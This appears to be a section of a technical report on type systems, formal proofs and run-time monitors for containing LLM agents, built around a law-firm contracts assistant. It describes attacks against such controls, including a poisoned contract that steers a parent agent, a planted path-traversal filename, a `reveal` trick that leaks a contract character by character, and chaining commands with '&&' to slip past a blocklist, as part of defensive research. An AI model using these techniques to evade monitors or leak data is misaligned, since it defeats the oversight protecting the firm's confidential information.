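With ELBA, an agent can also give a sub-agent narrower file permissions than its own. Zhou and colleagues describe an application that starts one sub-agent per customer, each with access only to that customer's data. If the contracts assistant holds `root`, a `Path` for the contracts folder, it can give the Acme sub-agent only `root // "acme"`. The `//` operator follows symbolic links, which are files that point to other locations, before it checks where the result lies. So a link planted in Acme's folder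 can't lead outside it. The library also has no operation that widens a `Path`. Zhou and colleagues contrast this with operating-system sandboxes, which confine a process to a fixed set of folders.

In LACUNA, a child can use whatever is in scope where the parent calls it. By default, this includes everything in the parent's scope and anything the parent has created since it started. If the parent opens the contracts folder in a block, a child called inside that block can use the folder too. The child may therefore have more permissions than its parent started with, but it can't have more than the parent holds when it makes the call.

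The developer can limit a child's access by putting the call in a separate top-level function and passing in only selected values. The child then loses access to the parent's local variables but keeps access to the program's other top-level definitions. If the firm had defined its mailer at the top level, the child might still be able to send email. Zhao and colleagues acknowledge that the type system enforces minimal permissions but can't determine what they should be.

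A sub-agent with limited permissions can still influence its parent. For example, a sub-agent that can only read might return text from a poisoned contract, and that text might lead the parent to send an email. ELBA can guard against this by running the sub-agent inside LIO's `toLabeled`, which seals its answer in a labeled value.

Odersky and colleagues expect TACIT to support the same kind of inheritance, but they left a full evaluation with several agents to future work.

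### When two monitors interfere

Suppose the law firm runs two monitors. The limit monitor enforces requirement C, that the assistant sends at most one email, by suppressing every email after the first. The archive monitor inserts a copy to the firm's archive before each email. The firm connects them in a chain, so the second monitor receives whatever the first outputs. The assistant then tries to send one email to the lawyer.

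| Order | After the first monitor | After the second monitor |
|---|---|---|
| limit, then archive | email to the lawyer | copy to the archive, email to the lawyer |
| archive, then limit | copy to the archive, email to the lawyer | copy to the archive |

In the first order, two emails go out, which breaks requirement C if copies count as emails. In the second, the limit monitor counts the copy as the first email and suppresses the original, so the archive contains a message that the lawyer never received. Both monitors work as designed, but the firm never decided whether copies count as emails.

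Monitors that only return verdicts avoid this problem. *Adventures in Monitorability* (2019) describes running them side by side on the same actions. If the policy requires every monitor to approve an action, a single "no" blocks it whatever the others return, so their order doesn't matter. But a monitor that counts actions still has to receive the joint verdict. If the limit monitor counts an email that another monitor blocked, it will block the next email even though none has gone out.

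Ligatti, Lujo Bauer and David Walker built Polymer, a monitoring system for Java programs that deals with both problems. *Policy Enforcement via Program Monitoring* (Ligatti, 2006) explains that each policy separates its decisions from its record-keeping. A function called `query` examines an attempted action and returns a suggestion, without side effects. A second function, `accept`, runs only when Polymer is about to follow that suggestion, so the limit policy would update its count there.

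When two policies must both apply, Polymer's conjunction combines their suggestions as follows:

1. If either policy suggests inserting an action, the insertion comes first. If both do, the policy listed first goes first.
2. Polymer checks the inserted action against the combined policy too. After the insertion, it submits the original action again.
3. If neither policy suggests an insertion, the more restrictive suggestion wins. From least to most restrictive, the options are to ignore the action as irrelevant, allow it, replace its result, refuse it with an error, or halt the program.
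4. If the policies suggest different replacement results, Polymer refuses the action with an error.

With the firm's two policies, Polymer would send the archive copy, count it, and then refuse the email to the lawyer, whichever order the policies were listed in. The outcome is now predictable, but the email to the lawyer is still blocked.

The firm could fix this with a filter, which hides chosen actions from a policy. If a filter hides archive copies from the limit policy, both messages go out and the limit applies only to the assistant's own emails. The archive policy needs a similar filter, because otherwise it would keep archiving its own copies forever.

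The order of policies still matters in some of Polymer's other combinations. In `Dominates`, the first policy applies to every action relevant to it, and the second applies only to the rest. `TryWith` follows the first policy if it allows the action or suggests an insertion, and otherwise follows the second. Ligatti used `TryWith` to combine a policy that allows only web connections with one that allows only mail connections, so the program could make either kind.

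### The cost of changing a rule

Ligatti tested Polymer on an email program called Pooka, which has about 50,000 lines of code. The policy was about 1,800 lines long, and enforcing it didn't require reading or changing Pooka's source code. One part of the policy checks a remote site once a day for a new version and loads it while the program is running.

However, Polymer intercepts only the actions that a developer listed before the program started, so a policy loaded later can't control any others. If the law firm's monitor intercepts email but not printing, the firm could quickly add a rule against sending email at night, but a rule about printing would take more work. The firm would also have to check how any new rule interacts with the old ones, as the archive example shows.

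Adding a rule to a program's types can require changes to many functions. Suppose the firm decides that every email needs a partner's approval, and it makes `send_email` require an `Approval` capability. Every function that calls `send_email` now has to obtain one, often by requiring it from its own callers, which then have to change as well.

Odersky and colleagues point out that older capability systems had to pass every capability down from the program's entry point, which usually meant restructuring existing code. Scala reduces this work in two ways. If a function declares a capability as a `using` parameter, the compiler fills it in at each call where one is available, although any function that passes it along must still declare it. Scala also allows global capabilities, which functions can use without receiving them as arguments.

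Much of the remaining work disappears when an agent writes a new script for each task, because the model can write each one to fit the new signature. Only the library, the surrounding application and any saved functions need repair, and the compiler reports the places that no longer fit. The firm could also put the approval check inside the body of `send_email`, which would leave the signature unchanged but turn the rule into a run-time check.

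Existing agents such as Claude Code and Copilot can connect to TACIT unmodified because TACIT uses the Model Context Protocol, a standard interface between agents and tools. The firm can then change the capability library without changing the TACIT server, and switch to another compatible agent without rewriting its typed tools.

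## Which safety requirements are hard or impossible to express as types?

Capability types and effect types record what code can do, but not how often or in what order it does it, or whether it finishes. They also can't distinguish a true answer from a false one. TACIT and ELBA could therefore accept a script that breaks requirement C (at most one email), D (an accurate summary) or E (a summary eventually arrives). Richer type systems can express C and part of E. D is much harder, because somebody would first have to define accuracy precisely enough for a machine to check.

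### Counting emails

A capture set in TACIT records whether code can use a capability, not how many times. A function that sends one email through `mail` has the capture set {mail}. A function that sends two has {mail} ∪ {mail}, which is also {mail}, so both functions have the same type. The `sendEmail` function that Odersky and colleagues wrote for their AgentDojo tests takes recipients, a subject and a body, and nothing in its signature limits how often a script can call it.

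Affine types can impose such a limit. A program can use a value of an affine type at most once, whereas a linear type requires exactly one use. The language Rust treats values as affine unless a programmer makes them copyable, so the law firm could write a single-use email permit like this:

```
fn send_email(permit: EmailPermit, to: &str, body: &str)

fn script(permit: EmailPermit) {
    send_email(permit, "lawyer@firm.example", "The summary is ready.");
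    send_email(permit, "lawyer@firm.example", "The summary is ready.");
}
```

The first call uses up the permit. The second call also needs one, so the compiler rejects the script before either email goes out. This works only if the library keeps the permit's constructor private, provides no way to copy a permit, and is the only way to reach a mail server. Ordinary Rust code can open a network connection without a permit, so the firm would also need a sandbox.

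| What the script does with its permit | Compiler's verdict |
|---|---|
| sends no email | accept |
| sends one email | accept |
| sends two emails in a row | reject |
| sends one email in each branch of an `if` | accept |
| sends an email inside a loop, but only for the last contract | reject |

The last script is harmless because its condition is true only once, but the compiler doesn't detect this, so the model would have to move the `send_email` call to after the loop. Permits also complicate error handling. If the mail server is down, the failed call uses up the permit, and the script can't try again unless `send_email` returns the permit with the error.

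An affine permit suits requirement C because the firm lets the assistant finish without sending an email. A linear permit would force the script to send one. *Token Budgets* (Khan, 2026) also uses affine rather than linear types, in a Rust library that controls how much agents spend on model calls. A program that discards part of its budget spends less, so the library doesn't need to make it use the whole budget.

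The permit limits a single script, not the assistant. If the runtime gives every script a new permit, the limit resets each time, as it does with a monitor that loses its count between scripts. The same problem arises if the lawyer starts a new session or if two copies of the assistant run at once. To enforce the requirement across sessions, the firm has to keep a lasting record of the permits it has issued and check it before issuing another. That check happens at run time, and a counter inside `send_email` could enforce the same limit without a permit.

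Khan's tests suggest that such a counter is enough for a single agent. A four-line Python counter stayed within budget in all 30 runs, as did the Rust library. The types became useful when a parent agent shared its budget among sub-agents running at the same time, which had caused 11 of the real overspending incidents in Khan's catalogue. Careless Python code overspent in all 30 runs, while three careful versions, including a Python counter with a proper lock, never did. The careless version doesn't compile in Rust. The Rust library still enforces the limit by subtraction at run time, and the types only ensure that no code spends the same money twice.

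### Limits on amounts and order

Suppose the firm also lets the assistant pay court fees of up to €500. If the payment function takes an `Int`, a script can pass it 50,000 as easily as 50. A refinement type adds a condition to an ordinary type:

{a : Int | 0 < a ≤ 500}

The compiler uses a solver to prove that every amount the script might pass meets the condition. If the fee comes from a document, the script has to test it first, and the compiler accepts a payment only in the branch where the test succeeded. Solvers handle some kinds of arithmetic much better than others, so the compiler may reject a script whose amounts are always within the limit. The condition also applies to each payment separately, so ten payments of €500 would be accepted. Limiting the total also requires a budget like Khan's.

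Developers can get part of the benefit without a solver by wrapping a number in a type whose only constructor checks its range at run time. In *TypePilot*, Sternfeld, Kucharavy and Dolamic (2025) had models use Scala's types this way. One task was to calculate an average age. When simply asked to write the function, all three coding models they compared wrote code that accepted negative ages. After a second model listed the weaknesses and a third rewrote the code with stricter types, two of the three versions handled negative ages correctly. One of those two allowed only ages from 0 to 120. The compiler can't check whether 120 is a sensible limit for a human age, and it would also have accepted 12 or 1,200.

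Capability types also ignore order. If the contracts script emails the lawyer before it saves the summary, it uses the same capabilities as before, but the message is false when she receives it. Typestate prevents this by giving an object a different type after each step:

```
save   : Draft -> Saved
notify : Saved -> Notified
```

A script can't call `notify` first, because `notify` needs a `Saved` value and only `save` produces one. These values should be affine too, meaning usable at most once, since otherwise a script could save once and notify the lawyer repeatedly. Session types apply the same idea to a conversation between two parties. A session type could require an agent to propose a change, receive a yes or a no, and make the change only after a yes. In both cases, the developer has to work out every permitted order in advance.

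Concordat, a Python library, enforces such protocols at run time because, Sikaroudi (2026) argues, a language model can't be type-checked. That is true when the model chooses one tool at a time, but a compiler can still check the order of calls inside a script the model has written. Concordat offers the model only the tools that are legal at the current step. Sikaroudi tested it on airline tasks where the policy required an explicit yes before a change, but simulated customers asked to confirm at first replied "just do it and stop asking". An ordinary agent made changes without an explicit yes in 13 of 50 tasks with gpt-4.1 and in 29 of 128 runs with Claude Haiku 5.5, while the Concordat agent never did.

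This result shows that Concordat enforces the order, but not that customers consented. The library unlocked the booking tools when a message contained "yes", "yep" or "yeah", and Sikaroudi counted violations with the same test, so it was guaranteed to find none. As Sikaroudi points out, "yes, but not that one" would also have passed. A button would be a better test of consent than a keyword, but the developer would still have to choose it. The rule also kept the agent from completing some tasks. With Haiku, 13 runs succeeded only for the ordinary agent, and in 11 of them the Concordat agent gave up and transferred the customer to a person.

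### A false summary

Requirement D is about what the text means. If a contract ends on 31 May and the summary gives 31 March, the summary still has the type `Classified[String]`, and the script that saves it does only what it is allowed to do.

A stricter type could catch some errors. The firm could have `summarise` return a record with a separate field for the end date, and require that date to appear in the contract. No solver can prove in advance that a model's answer will meet this requirement, so the library would have to search the contract while the script runs. The type would ensure that no script skips the search. This would catch a date the model invented, but not one it took from the wrong clause. For example, if the model returned 31 March as the end date when it was actually the last day for giving notice, the date would pass the check because it appears in the contract.

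To exclude that mistake, the firm would need a formal rule for finding any contract's end date. Contracts can end early, renew automatically or depend on an event, and lawyers sometimes disagree about what a contract means. A type can express such a rule only after someone has made it precise.

### What a true summary gives away

An accurate summary raises a different problem, because it reveals something about the contracts. Suppose the firm's insurer asks how many of them contain a penalty clause. Noninterference would forbid any answer, because the number depends on the contracts. Answering would require declassification, a deliberate exception that releases chosen information from confidential data.

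In Odersky and colleagues' design, the method for this is `reveal`, which unwraps the content for code with a permission that the agent never receives:

```
def reveal(using permission: CanAccess[T]): T
```

A user with the right clearance could hold the permission. The programming interface that TACIT gives agents is stricter and has no `reveal` method.

It would be risky to give the agent even a narrow permission. As the signature stands, the permission depends only on the type of the content. Suppose the firm gave the assistant a `CanAccess[Int]` so that it could report the number of penalty clauses. The assistant could then write this:

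```
text.map(t => t.charAt(0).toInt).reveal
```

The pure function inside `map` turns the first character of a contract into a number, which `reveal` then releases. The assistant could extract the whole contract by repeating this for each character. The types can't distinguish a count from a coded letter because both are whole numbers.

A safer method is to put the whole calculation in a trusted function that takes a set of contracts and returns only the count. But if the script chooses the set, it can pass in one contract at a time and learn which ones have the clause. The firm would have to choose the set itself or require a minimum size, and it would also have to decide whether the insurer should have the number at all.

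Summaries from TACIT's trusted local model stay wrapped, and the lawyer, not the model, decides whether to send them to anyone. The firm could ask the model whether a summary is fit for release, but a sentence planted in a contract might influence the answer. Odersky and colleagues suggest attaching run-time checks on declassification to the library's functions, but leave this to future work.

### A script that never finishes

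The simplest way to break requirement E is to do nothing. The firm could prevent this by requiring every script to return a `Receipt`, a value that only the function for saving summaries can create. A script that returned without saving anything would then have the wrong type. But the compiler would accept this function:

```
def deliver(): Receipt = deliver()
```

The function calls itself forever, so it never has to produce a receipt. Haskell accepts an equivalent function. Zhou and colleagues describe a `BibIO` program as one that eventually produces a value, but Haskell's types don't ensure that it ever does. In their conclusion, they list termination, single-use authorisations and resource limits as things that richer types could add to ELBA.

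A total language accepts only functions that finish on every input. Typically, a function may call itself only on something smaller, such as the remaining contracts in a list. Lean, a language for writing proofs that a computer can check, normally applies this rule because its proofs are also programs. Without the rule, a function that called itself forever could count as a proof of any false statement.

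A total language also rejects some programs that would have finished, since no procedure can always tell which ones do. And it rules out scripts that keep retrying until a server responds. Such a script has to set a limit, such as ten attempts, and do something else if they all fail. Because it can't guarantee a receipt, its return type has to be "a receipt or an error", but a script that immediately returned an error would also have that type. The library could prevent this by letting only a failed attempt create the error. The types would then guarantee that the script either saves a file or tries to.

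This is weaker than requirement E in two ways. First, a total program can still take a century to finish, and no type can make the local model reply. A deadline is more useful, and a monitor can enforce one by stopping the script and alerting the lawyer. Second, the requirement applies to the agent and not just to its scripts, and the model may never submit a script that passes the check. Concordat has a similar limit. It rejects any protocol with a dead end, so the agent can always reach a final step, but nothing makes the model take that step. The library stops the run after a maximum number of turns.

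### Checking a plan against its purpose

The receipt is a small example of a postcondition, a statement that must be true when a piece of code finishes. Meijer, in *Guardians of the Agents*, proposes using such statements to check everything an agent plans to do:

1. The model writes a plan in a restricted format before it reads any outside data.
2. Each tool has preconditions, which must be true before it runs, and postconditions, which are true afterwards. The plan has its own postcondition, which states what the task should achieve.
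3. A verifier tries to prove that the plan achieves this and obeys the security policy.
4. The plan runs only if the proof succeeds.

The policy can be more precise than TACIT's types. One of Meijer's examples forbids including text from fetched emails in the body of an outgoing message, but only if the recipient is outside the company. A similar rule would let the contracts assistant email the summary to the lawyer, which TACIT's compiler rejects. To apply such a rule, the verifier must be able to determine the recipient's address from the plan.

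Meijer also explains how a plan can pass the proof and still do the wrong thing. A user asks an agent to delete two files, `foo.txt` and `bar.txt`. The tool `delete_file` takes a pattern, and its postcondition is that no file matching the pattern remains. The plan's postcondition is that `foo.txt` and `bar.txt` are gone. The model writes a one-step plan, `delete_file("*.txt")`. The proof succeeds because deleting every text file deletes those two.

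The missing part is a frame condition, which states what must stay the same. Meijer adds one to the tool, stating that files that don't match the pattern remain, and concludes that the plan with `*.txt` no longer passes. But the plan's own postcondition needs a frame condition too. If it still requires only that `foo.txt` and `bar.txt` are gone, deleting every text file satisfies it. The plan's frame condition rules out the harmful version, and the tool's allows the verifier to prove that deleting the two files by name is harmless. Frame conditions are easy to leave out because a person who asks for two files to be deleted assumes the others will stay.

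A postcondition on the final state also can't express how the program reached it. In one set of Sikaroudi's runs, the ordinary agent changed a booking without consent in 13 tasks, and the benchmark gave 8 of them full marks because the final bookings were as expected. A plan verified only against the final bookings would have passed too. To express the consent rule, the specification would have to include the conversation history in the state.

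Meijer accepts that some checks will remain at run time, such as whether a position in a list exists. Planning before reading any data also makes the agent less flexible, as it does with CaMeL. Zhou and colleagues cite an open-source implementation of the proposal, led by Nada Amin. Meijer (2026) later extended the idea in a conference talk, *Return of the Theorem*, which described using solvers to check agents' plans against a company's formalised business rules. Business rules are a promising place to start because a rule like "no refund above €500 without a manager's approval" is already almost precise enough for a solver.

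### Cheaper proofs and the wrong specification

Odersky and colleagues considered full specifications for agents but preferred types, partly because precise specifications are "often unavailable or impractical". One practical obstacle has been the work of writing proofs, which has shrunk quickly. In 2025, Sternfeld and colleagues asked six open models to write code for tasks as simple as calculating a factorial in Stainless, a system for proving properties of Scala programs. None of the models could consistently produce code that compiled, and one answer used an annotation to avoid the proof.

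In September 2026, Anthropic published the first complete computer-checked proof of Fermat's Last Theorem, which states that aⁿ + bⁿ = cⁿ has no solution in positive whole numbers when n is greater than 2. Dozens of agents wrote 13 million lines of Lean in 11 days, with occasional high-level instructions from one researcher. Two months later, *Safely scaling multi-agent teams with Claude Fable 5.2* (Martin, 2026) reported that 1,000 agents had reproduced the proof in 28.7 hours without a researcher directing them. They used a third as many output tokens, and their proof was a seventh as long.

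The proof that a five-line script deletes only two files is tiny by comparison. The work of writing proofs is therefore no longer a convincing reason to reject full verification, at least for companies with access to the strongest models. Types still take less work for simple rules, because the model doesn't have to give the compiler a proof.

These results are much weaker evidence about whether a suitable specification is available. Fermat's Last Theorem fits on one line, and mathematicians have agreed on its meaning for centuries. Anthropic used a separate program to confirm that its agents had proved the theorem as stated in Mathlib, Lean's standard mathematics library. In the November experiment, people gave the agents the definitions and all 60 statements to prove, including the theorem itself. The law firm has no agreed statement of what makes a summary accurate, so its agents would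 have nothing to prove.

A model could write the specification too, but somebody would have to check that it had the right meaning. *Toward Safe LLM Agents* (Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues, 2026) reviewed 38 studies and concluded that specification is the bottleneck. On one benchmark, only 24.8% to 34.2% of language models' translations from ordinary language into a formal planning language had the correct meaning. The review rates most of the field's main findings as very uncertain, and newer models may well do better. But even a rare mistranslation matters, because the proof will succeed against the wrong rule and give no sign of a problem. VIGIL's mistranslated calendar rule caused a false alarm that somebody could notice, but a translation that made the rule too weak would cause no alarm.

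Better provers don't close gaps in a specification, and they can make those gaps more dangerous. A hostile model that can prove difficult theorems can also search for a harmful plan that meets the specification, then supply a valid proof. One defence is to test the specification by giving the verifier plans that are obviously wrong. If `delete_file("*.txt")` passes, the specification needs another condition. This method finds only the gaps that somebody thinks to test for.

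## How can the work be divided between compile time and run time?

A compiler can check anything that follows from a script's text. Checks that depend on where a file link points, who will receive an email or what the agent did earlier have to wait until the script runs. TACIT and ELBA divide the work this way. Their types require risky actions to go through library functions, which check at run time whether each action is allowed. Three other systems apply proofs to the rules that a monitor enforces, but not to the agent's own code.

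### One file access in TACIT

Suppose the law firm has marked the folder `contracts/signed` as confidential, and an ordinary file, `next.txt`, names the contract to read today:

```
requestFileSystem("contracts") { fs =>
  val name = fs.access("contracts/next.txt").read()
  val text = fs.access("contracts/signed/" + name).readClassified()
  println(text)
}
```

The compiler can't know what `next.txt` will contain. If an attacker has changed it to `../../personnel/salaries.txt`, the script has the same type as before. Odersky and colleagues therefore spread the protection over several stages:

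1. Compilation. The compiler establishes that the script can reach files only through `fs`, and that `fs` can't leave the block. It also prevents scripts from opening a folder inside `map`, because `requestFileSystem` needs a capability that a pure function can't hold.
2. Finding the file. When the script calls `access`, the library checks the path. It refuses anything outside `contracts` with a `SecurityException`, so the attacker's path fails here.
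3. Reading. `readClassified` checks that the file is in a confidential folder and returns the text in a wrapper. The compiler would also have accepted the ordinary `read` method, because a file's type doesn't record whether it is confidential. Only the library can refuse that call.
4. Printing. `println` accepts a value of any type, so the compiler allows the last line. The library sends the agent a placeholder instead of the text.

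The first stage gives a guarantee for every possible run, while the other three check only the current one. But the run-time checks depend on the first stage, because without it a script could open the file some other way and skip them. Anderson required a monitor to run on every attempt at access, and the type checker ensures this for Scala code.

TACIT's library likewise compares each command and network host with the list that the script requested. It also stops waiting for a command after 30 seconds by default, a limit that the types don't express. Odersky and colleagues suggest adding audit logs and rate limits to the same library functions in future. Those functions would be a natural place to count emails.

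ELBA needs run-time checks for the same reason. Zhou and colleagues check file paths while the script runs because a symbolic link could point somewhere new after the script has compiled. They rely on LIO to control information flow.

### VeriGuard: proving the filter

A monitor's rule is a small program, and it can contain mistakes too. Miculicich, Parmar and colleagues (2025), in *VeriGuard*, verify this program before the agent starts. The user describes a rule in ordinary English, and the system prepares it as follows:

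1. A language model writes a policy function in Python, along with formal constraints on the function's answers.
2. The model looks for ambiguities in the request and asks the user about them. If no user is available, it chooses the most plausible reading.
3. The model writes tests and corrects the function until it passes them or reaches a limit on attempts.
4. Nagini, a program verifier for Python, tries to prove that the function meets the constraints. If the proof fails, the model receives the error and tries again, up to a limit.

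For requirement C, that the assistant sends at most one email, the constraints might be:

{sent ≥ 0}  ok = may_send(recipient, sent)  {ok ⟹ sent = 0}

The first bracket is the precondition and the last is the postcondition. A proof would show that `may_send` never approves an email when `sent` is above zero, whatever the recipient.

At run time, a language model fills in the function's arguments from the agent's data, and ordinary code runs the function before each action. Nothing proves that the arguments are right, so if the model sets `sent` to 0 after the agent has already sent an email, the verified function will approve a second one. The law firm should take this number from a counter in the email tool and use a model only for arguments that ordinary code can't extract. Nothing proves that the constraints match the user's request either, and Miculicich and colleagues acknowledge that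 the user has to check them.

The researchers tested VeriGuard on Agent Security Bench, which includes prompt injections and poisoned memories. Without a defence, between 49.9% and 63.7% of attacks succeeded on average, depending on the model. No attacks succeeded with VeriGuard, or when a language model instead judged whether each action complied with the policy. VeriGuard's advantage was that the agent completed more tasks. With Claude Sonnet 4, for example, the agent completed 85.1% of its tasks under attack with VeriGuard and 68.3% with the model judge.

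These results don't show a benefit from the proof itself. In an experiment that added VeriGuard's components one at a time, successful attacks fell to zero before formal verification was added. The proof could still matter for inputs that neither the tests nor the attacks covered.

The response to a violation had a large effect on utility, as tests with Gemini 2.5 Flash show:

| Response to a violation | Attacks that succeeded | Tasks completed |
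|---|---|---|
| End the task | 0% | 0% |
| Block the action | 0% | 38.1% |
| Block only the suspicious tool call | 0% | 44.6% |
| Explain the violation and ask for a new plan | 11.9% | 62.1% |
| Block the tool call and ask for a new plan | 0% | 63.3% |

VeriGuard also made mistakes on Mind2Web-SC, which tests rules about what particular users may do on websites. It caught at least 99% of the violations, but between 5% and 9% of its refusals were wrong.

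### OpenShell: proving that a permission change stays within bounds

An agent may need new permissions mid-task, and a reviewer may not realise how much a change allows. NVIDIA addresses this in OpenShell, an open-source runtime that keeps agents in sandboxes. OpenShell denies everything by default and lets operators update a policy while the agent runs. A supervisor outside the agent's process checks outgoing requests, and according to NVIDIA, it can allow a read while blocking a write to the same service.

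OpenShell's policy prover checks the policy itself. According to NVIDIA, it uses formal logic to determine whether the permissions stay within boundaries set by the operator. A contributor to the project, zredlined (2026), in *feat(policy): spike policy envelope and narrowness prover*, proposes comparing each new policy with a maximum policy that a security team has approved. The solver looks for an action *x* such that:

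the new policy allows *x*, and the maximum policy forbids *x*.

Suppose the law firm's maximum policy only lets the assistant read hearing dates from a court's website, and a proposed change allows every kind of request to that address. The solver could then give the reviewer a concrete example of the problem, such as a request that writes to the site, which the maximum forbids. If the solver instead finds that the new policy allows nothing outside the maximum, that result covers every action its model can represent.

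A policy can be within the maximum and still allow far more than the task needs. The same proposal therefore includes a second check that compares the new policy with the current one and scores the added permissions. A firm could automatically accept small additions and send larger ones to a person.

Proofs are especially useful when an AI agent writes the policy. Google's *Securing the agentic era* (2026), which announces a similar verifier for policies written in a language called CEL, warns that an agent may fit a policy to the existing tests. The policy could then fail on inputs the tests don't include.

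OpenShell's proof is about permissions, so the supervisor still has to check the actual requests. As Sistla and colleagues point out, the proof also covers only single actions, so it can't rule out a leak that combines a permitted read with a permitted upload.

The reported evidence for the prover is a functional test. In an April submission, zredlined (2026) reports that an early version checked a sample policy and found a way to export data and a way around a write restriction. The test shows that the prover can detect such problems, but not how often it would catch a mistake in a real policy.

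### Tether: proving the policy engine

Tether, the system-call monitor that labels files, can handle sequences of actions. Its policy engine is written in Lean, so the proofs are about the same definition that runs as the monitor.

Some of the proofs hold for any Tether policy. For example, adding a rule that allows an action can't override another rule's denial, and changing the order of the rules doesn't change the verdict. A blocked action also leaves the recorded state unchanged, so an email that one rule blocks isn't counted by another.

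One of the seven properties that Sistla and colleagues proved for their 24-rule test policy is that secret data never enters the agent's context. The policy has four levels of confidentiality:

Public < Internal < Sensitive < Secret

Let *T* be the highest level of anything the agent has read. Part of the proof shows that *T* never rises above Sensitive:

1. At the start, *T* is at most Sensitive.
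2. Only reading a file or receiving network data can change *T*. If the new data has level *d*, *T* becomes the higher of *T* and *d*.
3. The policy allows these actions only if *d* is at most Sensitive, so the new *T* is at most Sensitive too.
4. Every other action leaves *T* unchanged.

Tether's proofs show that each permitted action preserves the property, so it holds after any number of actions. An earlier survey by Dantas and colleagues found that the guarantees of run-time monitors covered only single steps or short sequences. A language model writes Tether's proofs and Lean checks them, so a mistake by the model can't make a false property pass.

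The proofs don't cover the step in which Tether infers actions from system calls. Sistla and colleagues tested this step by fuzzing (trying many randomly generated cases). They generated sequences of file operations with known effects, carried out each operation by a randomly chosen method, and compared Tether's labels and verdicts with the correct ones. Fuzzing can reveal a method that Tether misses, but it can't prove that there are no others.

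Tether's false-alarm rate could be higher than 4.7% on unfamiliar work, because the researchers revised the policy's rules after trying them on runs from the benchmarks.

### A rule for dividing the work

The firm can decide where to put each check by considering what information it needs and whether anyone could undo a violation.

Checks that need only the script's text, the tools' signatures and the policy should happen before the script starts, because a rejected script hasn't changed anything and the model can safely try again. These include checks for leaks through branches that a particular run would skip.

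A check has to happen at run time if it depends on a live value, such as the contents of `next.txt`, or on history, such as the number of emails already sent. Types can still ensure that the script can't avoid the check.

How long a check can wait depends on whether the action can be undone. Tether can let a command change files before deciding, because the command works on a disposable copy. An outgoing request can't be undone, so Tether holds it in a proxy until the policy approves it.

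The resulting rule is to check in advance whatever the text and the policy determine, route everything else through a run-time check, and finish that check before any effect that can't be undone. For the contracts assistant, it gives the following division:

| Requirement | Before the script runs | While it runs | Can a violation be undone? |
|---|---|---|---|
| A: read only the contracts folder | Types send every read through the library, and a solver checks changes to permissions | The library checks each path | Only if the text hasn't left the firm's machines |
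| B: keep contract text from outsiders | Types allow only pure functions to touch the text | The library hides printed text, and a trusted function checks any release | No |
| C: send at most one email | Types send every email through one function | That function checks a lasting count before sending | No |
| D: write an accurate summary | Types require fields such as the end date | Code compares the fields with the contract, and the lawyer reviews the summary | Usually, until someone relies on it |
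| E: eventually deliver a summary | Types require a receipt for a saved file | A timer alerts the lawyer if the summary is late | The summary can still arrive, but the lost time can't be recovered |

For requirement C, a single-use permit could add an earlier check within each script. For D, the lawyer's review does most of the work.

### When the agent uses existing shell and Python tools

Many agents work through a shell, where they run existing compilers, package managers and Python scripts. Rebuilding all these tools as typed functions would take a lot of work, and the types still wouldn't control what happens inside each program. Sistla and colleagues add that a shell command's effects are hard to predict from its text, since the command may run a script or fill in variables whose values aren't known yet. Monitoring alone is a reasonable choice for such agents.

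The monitor should check the effects of commands, because rules about their text are easy to bypass. Zhou and colleagues cite a fault in the coding agent Claude Code in March 2026. When an agent joined several commands with `&&`, the software checked only the first against its list of forbidden commands. An agent can also get around a ban on reading a file by opening it with Python.

Another option is to have a language model judge each command. Sistla and colleagues compared Tether with Auto Mode, Claude Code's built-in judge, running on Claude Sonnet 5:

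| Monitor | Attacks stopped, of 344 | False alarms, in 1,590 harmless runs |
|---|---|---|
| Tether | 100% | 4.7% |
| Auto Mode with its default rules | 91.6% | 9.7% |
| Auto Mode with Tether's policy | 89.2% | 3.5% |

Auto Mode missed attacks hidden inside scripts, and even with Tether's policy it sometimes allowed requests to addresses that weren't on the approved list. But the comparison favours Tether because it leaves out the runs that Tether couldn't fully trace and model.

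Tether isn't yet a finished product. Its tracing tool slowed the experiments considerably and can read encrypted web traffic only if it goes to the simulated sites used in the tests.

Static proofs are useful even if nobody type-checks the agent's commands. An agent may write thousands of commands under one policy, so one proof about that policy covers them all and needs repeating only when the policy changes. The firm could also use both methods in one agent. Scripts that handle contracts would go through TACIT, while the shell would run under a monitor in a sandbox that doesn't contain the contracts.
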